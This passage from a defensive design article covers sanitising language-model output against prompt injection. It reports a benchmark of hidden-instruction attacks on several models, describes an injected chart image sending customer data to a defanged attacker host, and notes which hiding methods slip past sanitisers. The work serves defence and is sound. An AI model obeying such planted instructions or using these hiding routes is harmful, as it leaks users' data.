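Replacing `[.]` with a dot now gives `reports[.]example`, which still doesn't work. The restoring program would need the number of times other programs had defanged the address. Image proxies have a similar problem if two programs each put the proxy in front of an image's address, because the proxy then has to fetch the image through itself. A filter can avoid this by skipping addresses that already point to the proxy.

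The opposite mistake is to make something work again by accident. A later program may remove brackets during a general clean-up, or an editor may "correct" `hxxps`. GitHub's optional `normalize-closing-keywords` setting makes text work again on purpose. In a GitHub pull request, the words `Closes #123` can close issue 123 when someone accepts the change. Models sometimes put backticks around these words, which stops them from working, and the setting removes the backticks. But a model might have used the backticks deliberately, in a sentence explaining how to close an issue, and removing them would turn the explanation into a working command.

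Both problems become rarer if the application creates each version directly from the original answer, because no program then has to infer what an earlier one did.

### Measured effects on usefulness

Guo and Wei (2026), in *Hidden-in-Plain-Text*, measured both the protection and the drawbacks of sanitising text that a model reads. Their setting is close to that of the second model, but their results are only indirect evidence about the manager's screen.

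The study used 6,200 web pages built in the style of social media posts, with instructions hidden in them in five ways. Each page also had a harmless counterpart. A search system passed the most relevant passages, usually five, to a language model prompted to ignore any instructions in them. The models were Llama 3 in two sizes, Mistral 7B and Qwen2.5 14B, all old by 2026 standards.

The table shows how often, in per cent, a model followed the hidden instructions:

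| Where the instructions were | No defence | HTML and markdown sanitised | Unicode cleaned | All defences |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hidden text | 34.0 | 12.3 | 33.1 | 5.0 |
| Text placed off the screen | 30.1 | 9.8 | 29.3 | 4.6 |
| Alternative text of images | 27.8 | 11.1 | 27.0 | 4.8 |
| Labels for screen readers | 9.6 | 9.3 | 9.4 | 5.1 |
| Invisible characters | 23.2 | 23.0 | 7.8 | 4.2 |
| Average | 24.9 | 13.1 | 21.3 | 4.7 |

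Sanitising nearly halved the average, but it did almost nothing about invisible characters or screen-reader labels. Cleaning the Unicode dealt with most of the invisible characters. "All defences" adds a rule that every sentence of the answer must cite a passage, and the system regenerates any that don't, so the low figures in the last column don't come from sanitising alone.

The drawbacks were small. With sanitising and Unicode cleaning together, the share of questions the system could answer fell by about two percentage points (Guo and Wei give 1.8 and 2.2). The search results became slightly worse. Their mean reciprocal rank, which is 1 if the right page always comes first and 0.5 if it always comes second, fell from 0.462 to 0.450. Sanitising added 31 milliseconds to a typical response time of about one second.

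The results were similar on 2,350 real pages from blogs, forums and product documentation. Sanitising reduced the attackers' success rate from 22.7 to 12.0 per cent, and from 28.9 to 15.8 per cent when they adapted their wording.

The two-point loss was measured with sanitising and Unicode cleaning combined, but the table of success rates has no column for that combination, so it isn't clear exactly how much protection it gives. Guo and Wei used an automatic detector to determine whether a model had obeyed. They compared the detector with human judgements of what they describe as 1,200 answers, but the counts they publish add up to 1,400. The defences differ by enough that this probably doesn't change their order.

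About half of the attacks that still succeeded used instructions in the visible text. A sanitiser leaves such text in place because it looks like any other content. In the manager's case, removing the chart from the first answer wouldn't stop a second model from following an instruction that the first model copied into its summary.

Usefulness on the manager's screen could fall by more than two points. Guo and Wei's sanitiser removed hidden material and kept the visible text, whereas a link filter may remove something the reader wants. They also measured only whether the system can answer, without testing whether a reader can check the answer, so "Renewals rose to 84 per cent" would count as a success with or without the link to the report.

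The benchmark doesn't compare rewriting with blocking. A company could make that comparison with its own flagged answers, using invented customer data. One group of employees would receive the rewritten answers, and another would receive an error message and the chance to ask again. The company could measure how many employees in each group found the correct figure, how long they took, and how many believed an incorrect one.

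### One original, several copies

An application can serve all three readers by storing the original answer under restricted access and making a separate neutralised copy for each use. For the manager's question, the copies might look like this:

| Copy | Treatment of the link | Treatment of the chart |
|---|---|---|
| Original, for investigators | Unchanged, shown only as plain text | Unchanged, shown only as plain text |
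| Screen, for the manager | Works, because the site is on the allowlist | A notice that names `attacker[.]example` |
| Data, for the program | The full address in its own field | An entry with the reason for the refusal and no address |
| Text, for the second model | `[source 1]` | `[image removed]` |

The second model can't restore an address it never received. After it finishes, ordinary code replaces `[source 1]` with the approved link. An injection could still make the model attach the source to the wrong sentence, but it couldn't add a customer's name to the address.

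Patitas, a markdown library for Python, supports part of this design. A program parses the text once, applies a policy for what to remove, and produces the version it needs. According to Patitas' *LLM Safety*, the version for language models reduces each image to a label, so the chart would become `[image: Renewals]`.

Despite their names, `web_safe` and `llm_safe` are the same policy. It removes HTML, invisible characters and addresses such as `javascript:`, but not ordinary `https` images. The chart disappears for the model only because the last step prints images as labels, so a web page made with `web_safe` would still load it. The developer can add the `strip_images` rule for on-screen output, but an allowlist of hosts needs extra code because the ready-made rules that Patitas lists filter addresses by type, not by site.

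GitHub Agentic Workflows also keeps the original text for a time. According to the specification, sanitising is irreversible and GitHub doesn't preserve the original afterwards, but the file that the model's job passes to the publishing job still contains it. The sanitiser also logs the addresses it redacts, so a developer could see that it keeps redacting `reports.example`.

If the publishing job fails or a detector stops the output, someone can rerun the publishing step from the stored file, so a false alarm doesn't destroy the model's work. GitHub allows this only for people with `admin` or `maintain` rights to the project. They should first read the file as plain text, because rerunning the step could publish a real attack.

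Keeping the original also lets the application correct its mistakes. When the developer adds `reports.example` to the allowlist, the application can show last month's answers with working links. If a permitted site turns out to forward data to strangers, the application can disable links to it in old answers. Neither is possible after the company deletes the original, so how long it stores customer names also limits how long it can repair old answers.
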